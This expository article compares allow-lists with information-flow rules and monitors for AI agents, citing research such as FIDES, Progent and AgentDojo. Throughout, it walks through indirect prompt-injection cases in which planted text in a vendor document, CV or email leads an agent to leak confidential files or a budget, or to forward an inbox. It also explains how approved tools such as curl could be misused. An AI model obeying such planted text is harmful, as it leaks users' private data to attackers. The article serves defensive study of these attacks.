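# Information-flow rules and invariants for AI agents, compared with lists of permitted actions

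## How an agent acts and where a rule can stop it

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can request outside functions, such as reading a file, searching a mailbox, sending an email or paying a bill. Each request is called a tool call, and the model chooses both the function and its arguments. An agent's errors therefore have effects outside the conversation. People who deploy agents want some assurance about what the agents will do, especially when an agent handles text written by strangers.

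One way to get that assurance is to use a per-action allow-list, where a program judges each tool call only by its name and arguments and blocks any call the list doesn't permit. Another way is to write rules that depend on more than the single call. An information-flow policy governs where data may travel ("nothing from the payroll folder may reach an outside address"), and an invariant is a condition that must hold at every point of a run ("the agent never pays an invoice without a manager's approval"). All these rules take effect after the model requests a call and before the call runs.

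### The agent loop

The loop begins when a user types a request. An ordinary program, the application, adds the request to a conversation history, usually after a system message containing the developer's standing instructions. It sends this history to the model with a description of each available tool. The model returns text. If the text is an answer for the user, the loop ends. Otherwise it is a tool call, which the application can recognise by its fixed structure, typically in the data format JSON. The application runs the requested tool, appends the result to the history and queries the model again, so each query contains everything that came before it.

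*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) reduces this to a small formal model. The planner, the part of the agent that decides on the next step, can query the model, make a tool call, or finish and answer the user. The paper's basic planner passes the whole history to the model with each query and makes every call the model requests.

The model cannot send an email itself. It can only output a string that names `send_email` and fills in the arguments, and the application that receives the string does not have to send the email.

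### Why text in a document can work as a command

Every message in the history carries a role: system, user, assistant or tool. Before each query, the application flattens the history into a single string, with the roles indicated only by markers in the text. Developers intend the model to use these markers to tell the user's words, which it should obey, from the contents of a web page, which it should only read. But the model works by predicting how the string continues, and nothing in that mechanism enforces the distinction.

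In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which somebody types database commands into a web form. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which send the command and the visitor's input to the database separately, so that the database never runs the input as a command. A language model has no such separation between commands and input, and David C thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever prevent prompt injection as thoroughly.

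Experiments on how models tell the roles apart suggest the same thing. *The Illusion of Role Separation* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2025) found that fine-tuned models often relied on two shortcuts: the type of task and how close a passage was to the start of the input. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) found that models infer who is speaking more from how a passage is written than from its role marker.

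Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2024), in *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?*, put a number on the problem. They took harmless questions, such as what one calls a group of crows, and placed each question once among the model's instructions and once inside the text that the model had to process (a statement about a product launch, say, whose tone it had to classify). If the word "murder" turns up in the output, the model has answered the question. Their separation score is a simple fraction:

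separation score = (cases in which the model answers the question when it stands in the instructions but leaves it alone when it stands in the data) ÷ (all cases in which the model answers it when it stands in the instructions)

A model that never mistook data for instructions would score 100%. The GPT-4 of early 2024 scored 20.8% with a plain set-up and 95.3% with the best prompt wording, though GPT-4 had also helped to write the test set, which may have inflated its scores. Fine-tuning raised the average score of seven smaller open models from 37.5% to 95.5%, but the share of questions they answered when somebody properly asked them fell from 67.8% to 50.0%. These models are long out of date, and the figures mainly show how the obvious remedies behaved. A later attempt, *ASIDE* (2025), builds the distinction between data and instructions into the network by rotating the numerical representation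 of every piece of data through 90 degrees. The best separation score in its tests on Qwen3-8B, a small open model, was 71.4%.

An attacker can exploit the weakness without direct access to the agent. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants instructions in data that the agent will read later, such as a web page, an email or a shared document. Kai Greshake and colleagues introduced the attack in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides an instruction in a CV for the screening model to approve the candidate for interview. The weakness can also cause errors when nobody intends harm. Zverev and colleagues show an email assistant, instructed never to act on requests in emails, that replies to a friendly note because the note contains a request for confirmation.

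Model developers train against these attacks, and the training helps. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (He and Zharmagambetov, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts on 13 frontier models. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The developers have since released newer models, which may well do better. Still, even a 0.5% rate, which would be low for accidents, is rather high for attacks, because an attacker can try again.

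### The vendor's document

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, work through a small case that contains most of what is at issue between the different kinds of rule. Stripped to its main events, the run goes like this:

1. The user asks the agent to summarise a vendor's document and email the summary.
2. The agent reads the vendor's document. The text contains a planted instruction to send confidential data to an outside address.
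3. The agent reads a confidential file.
4. The agent requests an email to the outside address, with the contents of the file in the body.

Nothing has leaked up to event 4. Event 2 is what the user wanted. Event 3 is odd given the task, but an agent with access to confidential files presumably has it for a reason, and many honest requests would lead it to open one.

Event 4, the harmful step, is a call to `send_email(to, body)`, the same function that sends the email the user wanted. The text may not reveal the attack, since an attacker can plant an instruction to paraphrase the file or bury two figures from it in an otherwise ordinary summary. The address may reveal it. If the user is the only proper recipient, a check on the address is enough. But if the job is to send the summary to a partner firm, both the harmless email and the harmful one go to outsiders, and the check has to specify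 which outsiders may receive which contents. The two emails differ reliably in where the body came from. According to Palumbo and colleagues, the call may be safe when the body depends only on a public document and unsafe when it depends on both an untrusted document and a sensitive file.

### What a monitor can inspect

A monitor is code outside the model that intercepts each tool call and allows or blocks it before it takes effect. FORGE, built by Palumbo and colleagues, suspends the call, gathers the relevant facts, evaluates the rules, and then releases the call or returns a refusal to the agent with an explanation. The agent can continue after a refusal, perhaps by finishing the legitimate part of the job. A monitor can base its decision on the call itself, the origin of the data behind it, or the history of the run.

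A rule about the call itself can be checked using only the function's name, its arguments, and any fixed tables the rule refers to. Palumbo and colleagues tested one such rule, which lets the agent email only recipients whose security clearance is at least as high as its own. An unknown outside address has no clearance, so the monitor blocks event 4. It would also block an innocent summary sent to the same address.

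For a rule about origin, the monitor has to know what fed into the call. The usual method is to put labels on data and carry them forward to whatever derives from it (taint tracking). Palumbo and colleagues write such rules in Datalog, a language from database research, and the one for this case fits on a line:

`Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).`

The rule blocks action *a* if it sends something to an outsider, untrusted input has influenced it, and it carries sensitive data. Event 4 meets all three conditions because it depends on events 2 and 3. In a run without event 3, the rule allows the summary to be sent, even to an outsider. The rule is cautious because FORGE treats every message in the history that the model received as a possible influence on what the model wrote next. Even an honest summary would meet the three conditions if the model wrote it after opening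 the confidential file.

The history of the run contains facts that the arguments and the origin of the data do not. A sample rule from the same work denies a protected call unless the required approval is on record. For the vendor's document, a rule might block any email from leaving the company after the agent has opened a confidential file, until the user has confirmed the email. An approval usually adds nothing to an email's text, so a monitor that tracked only the sources of the text would not check for one. A monitor can easily use both kinds of evidence. Costa and colleagues use rules about labels, but note that their loop could also record the sequence of past actions and check conditions on it.

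### Enforcement outside the model

A developer could try to get the same behaviour by forbidding the model, in the system message, to reveal confidential data, or by training it to be better at ignoring commands inside documents. Palumbo and colleagues compared the system-message approach with a rule enforced by a monitor. Their agent, which ran on the small model GPT-4.1-mini, had an email tool and files graded from unclassified to top secret, and the planted instruction was disguised as a mandatory compliance audit. With a prompt that warned against exfiltration, the agent sent out top-secret merger plans in all five trials. With the monitor on, it leaked nothing in any trial across three configurations, and it still delivered a harmless internal report every time.

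Five trials of one attack on one small model are weak evidence of how often prompting fails in general, and judging by the competition figures, a stronger model would probably have resisted more often. The experiment is more useful for showing how a monitor differs in kind from prompting or training. Whether prompting or training works depends on how the model reacts to a particular wording, so one can measure only how often it works against the attacks somebody thought to try. The monitor's verdict depends on the call and the recorded facts. In the enforced runs, the model may be just as thoroughly deceived, and it requests the email, but the monitor blocks it. This is why David C advises designers to put more weight on deterministic safeguards around the model than on keeping malicious text away from it.

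A monitor enforces only its written policy, so it allows a harmful call if the policy permits it. A well-trained model may refuse to take a harmful action that no one had listed. A developer can use both a monitor and a well-trained model.

### AgentDojo

Most later measurements of these defences use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark built at ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs. It simulates four working environments, each with its own tools and invented data. A user task is a request such as paying a bill or counting the day's appointments, and an injection task is an attacker's goal. The benchmark pairs every user task with every injection task in the same environment, which gave 629 test cases in the first version.

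| Environment | Tools | User tasks | Injection tasks | Pairings | An attacker's goal |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, cloud drive) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 | Email a security code to the attacker |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 | Send a colleague a phishing link |
| Travel | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 | Book the most expensive hotel in Paris |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 | Transfer as much money as possible to the attacker |
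| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 | |

The attack text sits in places where an outsider could plausibly write, such as the body of an email, and where the agent will come across it while doing the user's task. After each run, a short program written for the task inspects the state of the environment: whether the money moved, whether the message went out. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against a language model as judge, on the ground that an injection good enough to fool the agent might fool the judge too. They report three figures:

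- **Benign utility** is the share of user tasks that the agent solves when there is no attack.
- **Utility under attack** is the share of pairings in which the agent solves the user's task without any harmful side effect.
- **Targeted attack success rate** is the share of pairings in which the attacker's goal comes about.

The attack success rate varies considerably with the wording of the attack. Against GPT-4o, the benchmark's main attack message succeeded in 45.8% of cases when it addressed nobody by name, 47.7% when it named both the user and the model correctly, and 23.7% when it addressed GPT-4o as Claude. A low attack success rate against a defence may therefore reflect a weak attack. The designers intended the benchmark to include new attacks as people devise them.

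AgentDojo's attack scores also need to be read with care. Costa and colleagues reviewed the attacks that the benchmark had counted as successes. For their basic planner with the rules switched on, AgentDojo reported 20, but they counted none. Across their tests, they discounted attacks for one of three reasons: the monitor had blocked the call, the policy allowed the action, or the injection had changed only the wording of some text. The first is a scoring error. The other two are successes in a sense, but the rules did not aim to prevent them. AgentDojo's data also have no labels, so anyone who tests an information-flow rule on the benchmark has to add them.

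AgentDojo's set of tasks has grown since 2024. An extension, *agentdojo inspect*, added attacks that attempt mass data theft in the Workspace environment, and the maintainers merged them into the main version. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 pairings, so scores from different years are not always based on the same cases. Researchers still use AgentDojo widely. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), for example, tests 13 models from six providers on it. *StepGuard* (2026) tests a guard model that checks calls before they execute. It also uses a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which has longer workflows and includes outside text with instructions the agent should follow. Such text is difficult to handle for any rule that treats all outside text as suspect.

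## The case for listing permitted actions

The simplest policy a monitor can enforce is a per-action allow-list, under which it refuses any call not on the list (default-deny). For the vendor's document, the list might include a tool for reading files and a tool that emails only the user. Because the agent has no tool for emailing anyone else, it can't email a file to an attacker, even if the model tries to follow the planted instruction.

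The list needs no labels on data and no record of the run. Its author can read it through in a few minutes, and can test it by trying calls and looking at the verdicts, since the same call always gets the same verdict. Strands Agents' *Cedar Authorization*, a documentation page for a toolkit for building agents, gives an example in which the whole policy is one line:

`permit(principal, action == Action::"search", resource);`

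The agent in the example has a search tool and a tool that deletes records. A user asks it to search for quarterly reports and then delete a record. The monitor allows the search and blocks the deletion, because deletion isn't on the list of permitted actions. Nobody had to foresee the deletion or write a rule against it.

### Least privilege

The reasoning behind such lists is much older than language models. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out eight design principles for protection mechanisms. Under one of them, least privilege, every program and user should work with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. This limits the damage from an accident or error. It also shortens the investigation when someone misuses a privilege, because fewer programs hold it.

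"The Protection of Information in Computer Systems" credits E. Glaser in 1965 with the principle that a system should refuse access unless a rule grants it. The paper argues that this makes mistakes easier to notice. If someone forgets to list a permission, a legitimate user is refused access and somebody soon fixes the list. A forgotten prohibition lets the forbidden access succeed, and in normal use people may not notice. The argument seems especially strong for agents, because their developers keep adding tools, and under default-deny an agent can't use a new tool until somebody decides to allow it.

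Saltzer and Schroeder also wanted protection mechanisms to be small enough for people to inspect line by line, and they wanted every access to be checked. An allow-list is easily small enough to inspect. Whether every access is checked depends on how the list is installed, because it doesn't restrict a tool that the agent can reach by some other path.

Recent guidance from security practitioners ranks default-deny for tool calls above every other architectural pattern for securing agents, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI agent’s system prompt is not a security control*. Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services (AWS) and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, wrote the guidance with three other AWS specialists. AWS's *Agentic security* identifies it as a chapter in the SANS 2026 Cloud Security Exchange eBook and presents it as an extension of established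 practice, including least privilege. AWS has a commercial interest in the advice because it sells a product that uses default-deny, but the advice does follow from the principles of 1975.

Rittenhouse and Johnson offer the list as one of several defences. According to Help Net Security, they also want a human checkpoint for high-impact actions, and they want no single agent to combine access to sensitive data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally, as the agent that reads the vendor's document does.

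### Conditions on arguments

A list of tool names can't distinguish a $20 refund from a $20,000 one, because both use the same refund tool. Modern lists therefore also put conditions on the tools' arguments. Developers often write these conditions for a policy engine, a program that evaluates access rules separately from the application. The SANS and AWS guidance names two ways to do this at scale: Cedar, an open-source policy language from AWS, and Open Policy Agent, a general-purpose engine with its own rule language, Rego.

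AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains how the company uses Cedar in its hosting service for agents. A gateway sits between the agent and its tools and blocks every call that no rule permits. One sample rule permits a bulk discount if the customer has Platinum status and the order contains at least 50 items, unless the order includes limited-edition or seasonal products. The customer's status comes from a login token, which the model cannot alter. The quantity and product types come from the model's call, and the rule limits them to acceptable values. If a `permit` rule and a `forbid` rule both match, the `forbid` rule wins, regardless of their order. The gateway also doesn't show the model any tool that the policy would always refuse.

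Cedar has no loops or stateful operations, which makes it possible to translate a policy into a mathematical formula and prove things about it before deployment. In an example from AWS, the old version of a discount rule refused the discount on all limited-edition products, and the new version refuses it only if the order also exceeds 200 units. An order of 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, and the analysis reports the new policy as more permissive, even though the added condition looks like a tightening. The same analysis catches a rule that can never permit anything because it requires a customer to be both Gold and Platinum.

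Nobody can prove anything comparable about a warning in a system message. The lack of state is also a limitation, since a rule that caps each refund at $500 does not cap the day's total unless another program supplies the running total.

### Progent: a list for each task

The right list also depends on the task. An agent needs an email-sending tool to send Alice an update, but the same tool is an unnecessary risk when the user only wants a summary of unread messages. A single list for both tasks has to include the tool, and writing a new list by hand for every request would remove most of the benefit of using an agent. In *Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025), a language model writes the list for each task and an ordinary program enforces it.

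Each rule in Progent has the form

`allow | forbid  tool  when { conditions },  fallback action`

The conditions can compare an argument with a value, test whether it belongs to a set, check the length of an array or match text against a pattern. The fallback is what happens after a refusal: the run ends, the user decides, or the agent receives a message. The default is a message that explains the refusal and tells the agent to carry on with the user's task by other means. In this notation, a policy for the vendor's document might look like this:

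```
allow read_file  when { path == "vendor.pdf" }
allow send_email when { to == "user@firm.example" }
```

Progent checks each call against the rules for that tool, trying the `forbid` rules before the `allow` rules. The first rule whose conditions hold decides the outcome, and if none hold, Progent blocks the call. The attack here fails at two steps, because the agent may not open the confidential file or write to the outside address. In the simplest version of the example, a well-fitted list therefore does at least as well as a rule about the origin of the data, without anyone having to label the data.

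Progent's model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of available tools, before the agent has read anything an attacker could have touched. For some requests, that first policy isn't enough. Shi and colleagues describe a user who asks the agent to carry out the to-dos in a particular email. At first, the policy can permit only the search for that email. The email asks for a summary of recent messages to be posted to the user's Slack account, so the agent now needs permission to read mail, look up the account and post. Once the agent has found the account name, the policy can restrict posts to that account. But one of the recent messages contains a planted instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. The agent thus encounters both the task's need for new permissions and the attacker's request for one in the text of emails.

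Progent updates the policy in steps. A model first decides whether the latest tool call is of a kind that might require an update. It sees the call but not the result, which is where an attack would be. If the answer is yes, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy. An SMT solver, which is a program that determines whether any values satisfy a logical formula, then compares the proposal with the old policy. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. The proposed policy P′ is a narrowing if

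A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

and otherwise it is an expansion. The solver can decide this because the rules are symbolic. For a given tool, a policy allows the arguments *v* if no `forbid` rule's conditions hold for *v* and at least one `allow` rule's conditions do. If Φ stands for that formula, the update is a narrowing when, for every tool,

for all *v*: Φ(P′, *v*) ⇒ Φ(P, *v*)

An update is an expansion if the new policy allows even one call that the old one refuses. Replacing one permitted recipient with another is therefore an expansion, even though the list does not get longer. Narrowings take effect immediately, while expansions wait for approval, so the set of allowed calls can only shrink between approvals. Shi and colleagues call this property monotonic confinement. The planted instruction may lead the model to propose adding `send_email`, but the addition has no effect until somebody approves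 it.

### How well Progent did

When GPT-4o both acted as the agent and wrote the policies, Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. On both benchmarks, the agent completed about as many of the user's tasks as before. An older defence that removes whole tools before the run did worse on both measures, because it ignores the arguments of tool calls.

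These figures don't measure the property that Progent's design guarantees. To simulate a careless user, Shi and colleagues had the system approve every expansion automatically, so the solver's verdict made no difference to what the agent could do. The 1.0% is evidence that GPT-4o writes good policies and mostly continues to do so when it reads an attacker's text. When the researchers turned off policy updates, the rate was 2.5%. Automatically refusing every expansion gave the lowest rate of the fully automatic settings. Human review brought the rate to zero, but that test assumed a reviewer alert enough to reject a malicious address.

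Approval need not be a great burden, since only 6% of the policy updates on AgentDojo were expansions. But many of the benchmark's tasks state clear goals in the request, which is the easiest situation for a list written in advance. An agent with vaguer instructions would presumably have to ask for approval more often.

The experimenters also attacked the policy writer, for example with planted text that told it to allow all tools. The attacks' success rate rose only slightly. Most of the remaining failures on ASB involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled legitimate ones. On AgentDojo, the experimenters left out two attacks that steer the agent towards a different but genuine hotel, because a list that permits the hotel booking the user asked for cannot stop them.

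*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) argues that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that people make errors when they write these by hand. It also argues that Progent does nothing about attacks on the agent's text output, and that an adversarial tool result may lead the update mechanism to relax the rules. The approval step in Progent's current version answers this last objection, provided that the approver can tell good expansions from bad ones.

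### The confused deputy

A deeper objection comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which describes an accident at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Users of its compiler, a program that translates code, could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in its own directory, SYSX, so the operators had given it permission to write there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user who had come across the billing file's name entered it as the destination for the debugging output. Because the compiler was allowed to write in SYSX, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

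Every program involved had done what its permissions allowed. A user induced the compiler to use its legitimate authority for a purpose its owners never intended. According to Hardy, this happened because the compiler acted with authority from two sources, its owners and the user, and could not specify which one it was using when it opened a file.

He then considers the obvious fixes. The compiler can't refuse to write to all other directories, because users have good reasons to put output there. It can't refuse everything in SYSX, because some users may legitimately write to files in it. Refusing only the billing file by name would leave the directory's other sensitive files exposed. Meanwhile, Tymshare's rules for opening a file had grown to fourteen logical operators. Each new permission made some previously secure program insecure, and each new restriction broke a program that had worked.

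Hardy's remedy was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and authorises its holder to use it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file, and the compiler would use it to write the debugging output. A user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for that file to give the compiler.

An agent is in much the same position as the compiler. It has the user's authority to read files and send email, but it takes suggestions about which files to read and which addresses to use from documents that strangers wrote. An allow-list checks whether the agent has the authority to act, but not on whose behalf it is acting. The agent's case is arguably worse, because the compiler's programmers could have rewritten it to keep the two sources apart, whereas a language model receives the user's and the stranger's words in a single string.

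Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026) reports that Ariel Fogel, a researcher at Pillar Security and a contributor to the security project OWASP, described a similar problem in a June 2026 conference talk on prompt injection. He said that in some attacks allow-lists had made exploitation easier, because the commands the agent needed were already approved. The article names no incidents, so it is hard to judge how often this happens. A developer might, for instance, approve the command-line program `curl` so that a coding agent can download documentation without asking each time. The agent could then also use `curl` to upload files without asking.

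### A legitimate recipient and the wrong content

A defender of lists would reply that the `curl` entry was too loose. The developer should have approved downloads only from named sites, just as the policy for the vendor's document named one file and one recipient. This is a good reply, because conditions on a tool call's arguments stop many attacks. Most of AgentDojo's attackers want a payment to an unfamiliar account or a message to an unfamiliar address, and such conditions catch those. Progent's results largely measure how well this approach can work.

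It works less well when the user's own task requires the dangerous combination. Suppose the user asks the agent to compare the vendor's quote with the firm's confidential budget, and then to email the vendor some questions about the price. The tightest list that still permits the job is something like this:

```
allow read_file  when { path in ["quote.pdf", "budget.xlsx"] }
allow send_email when { to == "sales@vendor.example" }
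```

The quote contains a planted request to mention the most the firm could pay. The agent reads two permitted files and sends one email to a permitted address, and the body of that email reveals the budget. Shi and colleagues acknowledge that attacks that stay within the least privilege for the user's task are outside Progent's scope.

The list could also restrict the body of the email. A pattern that blocks the budget figure in digits will miss "a little under half a million". Allowing only a few prepared messages would stop nearly every leak, but the agent could no longer write the questions it was asked to write. Sending every outside email to the user for approval is more promising, and may well be the best answer for a single email to a single vendor. However, AWS warns that people grow tired of approving when they have to do it too often. The person approving also has to recognise,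 unaided, that a phrase in the email derives from the budget.

The list's author can therefore withhold either the budget file or outside email, in line with the advice to keep sensitive data, untrusted content and external communication apart. This is safe, but the user has to do the task some other way. Palumbo and colleagues object to blanket restrictions of this sort, such as a ban on all external email, because they disable legitimate work. Alternatively, the list's author can allow both and accept that the leak will happen if the model follows the request.

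Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, provide a rough measure of how poorly the type of action separates attacks from honest work. They replayed recorded AgentDojo runs by GPT-4o against five general rules, each of which required some approval before a risky action such as a payment or an outgoing message. The recordings contain no approvals, so in practice the rules flagged every action of a risky type. They flagged 70.1% of the successful attacks and 29.3% of the runs without an attack. In the Banking environment the figures were 97.4% and 79.2%, since honest banking tasks also consist largely of moving money. There were only 123 honest runs, and a list fitted to each task would do much better than these rules. But it would do so by using the file names and addresses in the call, and in the budget example those are the same whether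 the email is honest or not.

Saltzer and Schroeder had already distinguished the two problems in 1975. Most of the systems they surveyed controlled who could obtain a piece of information. Saltzer and Schroeder treated control over what happens to the information afterwards as a separate, more demanding level of protection. They compared it to the "Top Secret" stamp on a document, which restricts what even a reader entitled to see the document may do with it. ADEPT, one of the few computer systems of the time that attempted this, tracked the classification of everything a program read and marked the program's output with the highest of those classifications.

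## The case for rules about where data may flow

In the budget example, the list permits every action, and the leak happens when data passes from one action to the next. An information-flow rule restricts how that data moves. The agent may read the budget and email the vendor, but it may not put anything derived from the budget in the email. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives a similar rule, that data from customer A should never go to customer B. An agent that serves both customers has to read both accounts and write to both addresses, so its owner can't enforce this rule by removing a file or an address from a list.

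Most of the theory dates from the 1970s, when several people could share one computer and often ran programs they had not written and could not check.

### The confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who gives private data to someone else's program, called a service. The customer can restrict which files the service opens, but the service needs some of the data to do its job and may pass it on to the program's owner. Lampson called preventing this the confinement problem. He noted that customers can see wrong output and complain about it, but a leak usually leaves no sign.

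In "A Note on the Confinement Problem" (1973), Butler Lampson wanted a method that could confine any program, and he accepted that some programs that work when free would stop working under confinement. People who use flow rules for agents make a similar tradeoff. They assume nothing about how the model will behave, and they accept that the rules will block some legitimate tasks.

Lampson listed ways the service could leak data. It could write to a file in its owner's directory or send the owner a message. It could also encode the data in its bill, which is harder to prevent because the owner has to receive the bill. Lampson called this a legitimate channel, and the email to the vendor is another. His remedy was to let the customer determine everything that goes into such a channel. For the agent, that would mean the user dictates the email. He also described covert channels, which nobody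 intended for communication. For instance, a service might vary its load on the machine so that another program can infer the data from the machine's performance.

Lampson proposed that when a confined program calls a program the customer doesn't trust, the called program must be confined too, so the restriction follows the data. The simplest rule would forbid a confined program to call any other program, but he thought this quite impractical.

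### Secrecy and integrity

The American military faced a pressing version of this problem. According to Cryptosmith's *MLS Introduction*, ordinary operating systems could usually keep users' programs apart, but they could not stop someone with a low clearance from tricking a Top Secret user into releasing secrets through a Trojan horse, a program with a hidden function. When the Top Secret user runs the program, it opens a Top Secret file with that user's authority and copies it to somewhere the attacker can read it. The instruction planted in the vendor's document works the same way, except that the attacker supplies only text, which the agent then carries out.

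Bell and LaPadula (1973), in *Secure Computer Systems*, began the mathematical model that became the standard answer. In its developed form, the model assigns a security level to every subject (a running program acting for a user) and to every object (such as a file), and imposes two rules:

subject *s* may read object *o* only if level(*o*) ≤ level(*s*)

subject *s* may write to object *o* only if level(*s*) ≤ level(*o*)

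The read rule is ordinary clearance. The write rule deals with the Trojan horse. A program running at Top Secret can read the file but can't write to anything below Top Secret, so the copy never reaches the trickster. Information can only move upwards, even when the program misbehaves.

Bell (1974), in *Secure Computer Systems*, a later volume of the same work, made two changes that matter for agents. First, the system now recorded a current security level for each subject, so it could check a new request with a single comparison instead of comparing it with every object the subject was using. Second, it exempted trustworthy subjects from the write rule, provided somebody had demonstrated that they would not leak information. Nobody can yet demonstrate that about a language model that reads strangers' text, so an agent has to count as an ordinary subject.

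These rules protect secrets but not accuracy. A program with no clearance may write to files at higher levels, so it could fill a Top Secret file with nonsense. MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), which introduced what is now called the Biba model after its author, addressed this problem. It defined integrity as the assurance that a system will perform as its creator intended, and it separated direct threats, such as overwriting a program, from indirect ones, such as supplying bad data that the program will later use. Prompt injection is an indirect threat in this sense. According to the report, guarding against indirect threats requires knowing both where a piece of information originally came from and the path it took.

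The best-known of the report's policies, strict integrity, turns the secrecy rules upside down:

*s* may read *o* only if integrity(*s*) ≤ integrity(*o*)

*s* may write to *o* only if integrity(*o*) ≤ integrity(*s*)

A trusted program may not read untrusted data. In the example, this rule would be safe but useless, because the agent could not open the vendor's document at all. The report also offered a low-water-mark policy. Under this policy, according to lecture slides from Purdue University, a subject may read data of lower integrity, but its own integrity then drops to the level of that data. The agent could open the vendor's document, but afterwards it would have only the authority appropriate to the vendor's text.

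A system that provides both kinds of protection needs two separate labels. Ray (2018) explains in lecture notes that if one label serves both, the two models impose opposite constraints and no information can flow between levels.

### The order on labels and the join

*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) put such schemes into one mathematical form, which consists of a set of labels, an order on them and a way of combining them. The designers of agent monitors still use this form.

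The notation ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂ means that data labelled ℓ₁ may flow to a place labelled ℓ₂. If the only confidentiality labels are public and secret, then public ⊑ secret, because public data may go into a secret file but secret data may not go into a public one. If the integrity labels are trusted and untrusted, then trusted ⊑ untrusted, because a place that accepts untrusted data can also accept trusted data. In both cases, the higher label is more restrictive.

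The order has to be transitive. If a program may copy *a* to *b* and then *b* to *c*, it can in effect copy *a* to *c*, so a rule that forbade only the direct copy would be easy to evade. Transitivity also means that if every operation respects the order, so does any sequence of them. A list of permitted actions lacks this property, as the budget example shows.

Data derived from two sources needs a label too, and this is the join, written ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂. It is the least upper bound of the two labels, which means that it satisfies two conditions:

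- ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ and ℓ₂ ⊑ ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂, so the result is at least as restricted as each source;
- if ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₃ and ℓ₂ ⊑ ℓ₃, then ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊑ ℓ₃, so the result is no more restricted than the sources require.

Costa and colleagues work this out for labels that are sets of people. Suppose that a confidentiality label lists everyone who may read a piece of data. Anne, Bill and Carl (A, B and C) may read one document, and Bill, Carl and Dora (B, C and D) may read another. A summary of both documents may reveal something from either, so only people entitled to both should see it:

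{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

The label {B} would also be safe, but it would exclude Carl for no reason, so the second condition rules it out. A label with fewer readers is stricter and ranks higher in the order, so *S* ⊑ *R* means that everyone in *R* is also in *S*.

An integrity label can instead list everyone who may have written part of the data. If A, B or C could have written to one document and B, C or D to the other, then any of the four may have had a hand in the summary:

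{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∪ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C, D}

As more sources go into a result, its list of readers can only shrink and its list of possible writers can only grow. A system that tracks both lists gives each result one label for readers and another for writers, and joins each kind separately.

Denning shows that several pieces of data may each flow to a destination exactly when their join may. A monitor can therefore keep one running label for everything an agent has read and compare it with the destination's label, without recording each item or the order in which the agent read them.

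Denning distinguished fixed labels from labels that change with an object's contents, and argued that a practical system needs some fixed ones. If users' clearances rose to match whatever they read, an unclassified user could get a higher clearance by reading a Top Secret file. For an agent, the recipients' rights are fixed and the conversation's label changes.

She also found a hole in ADEPT, the system that marked a program's output with the highest classification of any data the program had read. According to its published description, a program with Top Secret clearance could write anything it had read to an existing unclassified file, and the file kept its old classification. Careful labelling inside the system therefore gives little protection unless something also checks the label against the destination.

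### The tracking loop in FIDES

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, applies this scheme to the agent loop. Its simplest version tracks one label for the whole conversation, here called the context label. The paper writes the planner and the loop around it as separate algorithms. Merged and put into words, they run as follows:

```
 1  receive a message m with label ℓ
 2  add m to the history
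 3  context := context ⊔ ℓ
 4  if m is from the user or is a tool result:
 5      query the model with the history; label its reply "context"
 6  if m is a tool call:
 7      if the policy refuses the labelled call: stop
 8      run the tool
 9      new := label of the call ⊔ labels of its arguments
               ⊔ labels of all data the tool may read
10      put the label "new" on the result and on all data
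        the tool may write
11  if m is an answer: return it, with its label
```

The run starts at line 1 with the system message and the user's request, which are normally labeled trusted and public, the lowest label. Tool results can introduce other labels. A tool can label its result as a whole or label each field separately, so an email's sender and body can have different labels.

Line 3 combines the context label with the label of the new message. The context label can rise but never fall. Because a higher label means less trust, this works like the low-water-mark policy, under which a subject's integrity can only decrease.

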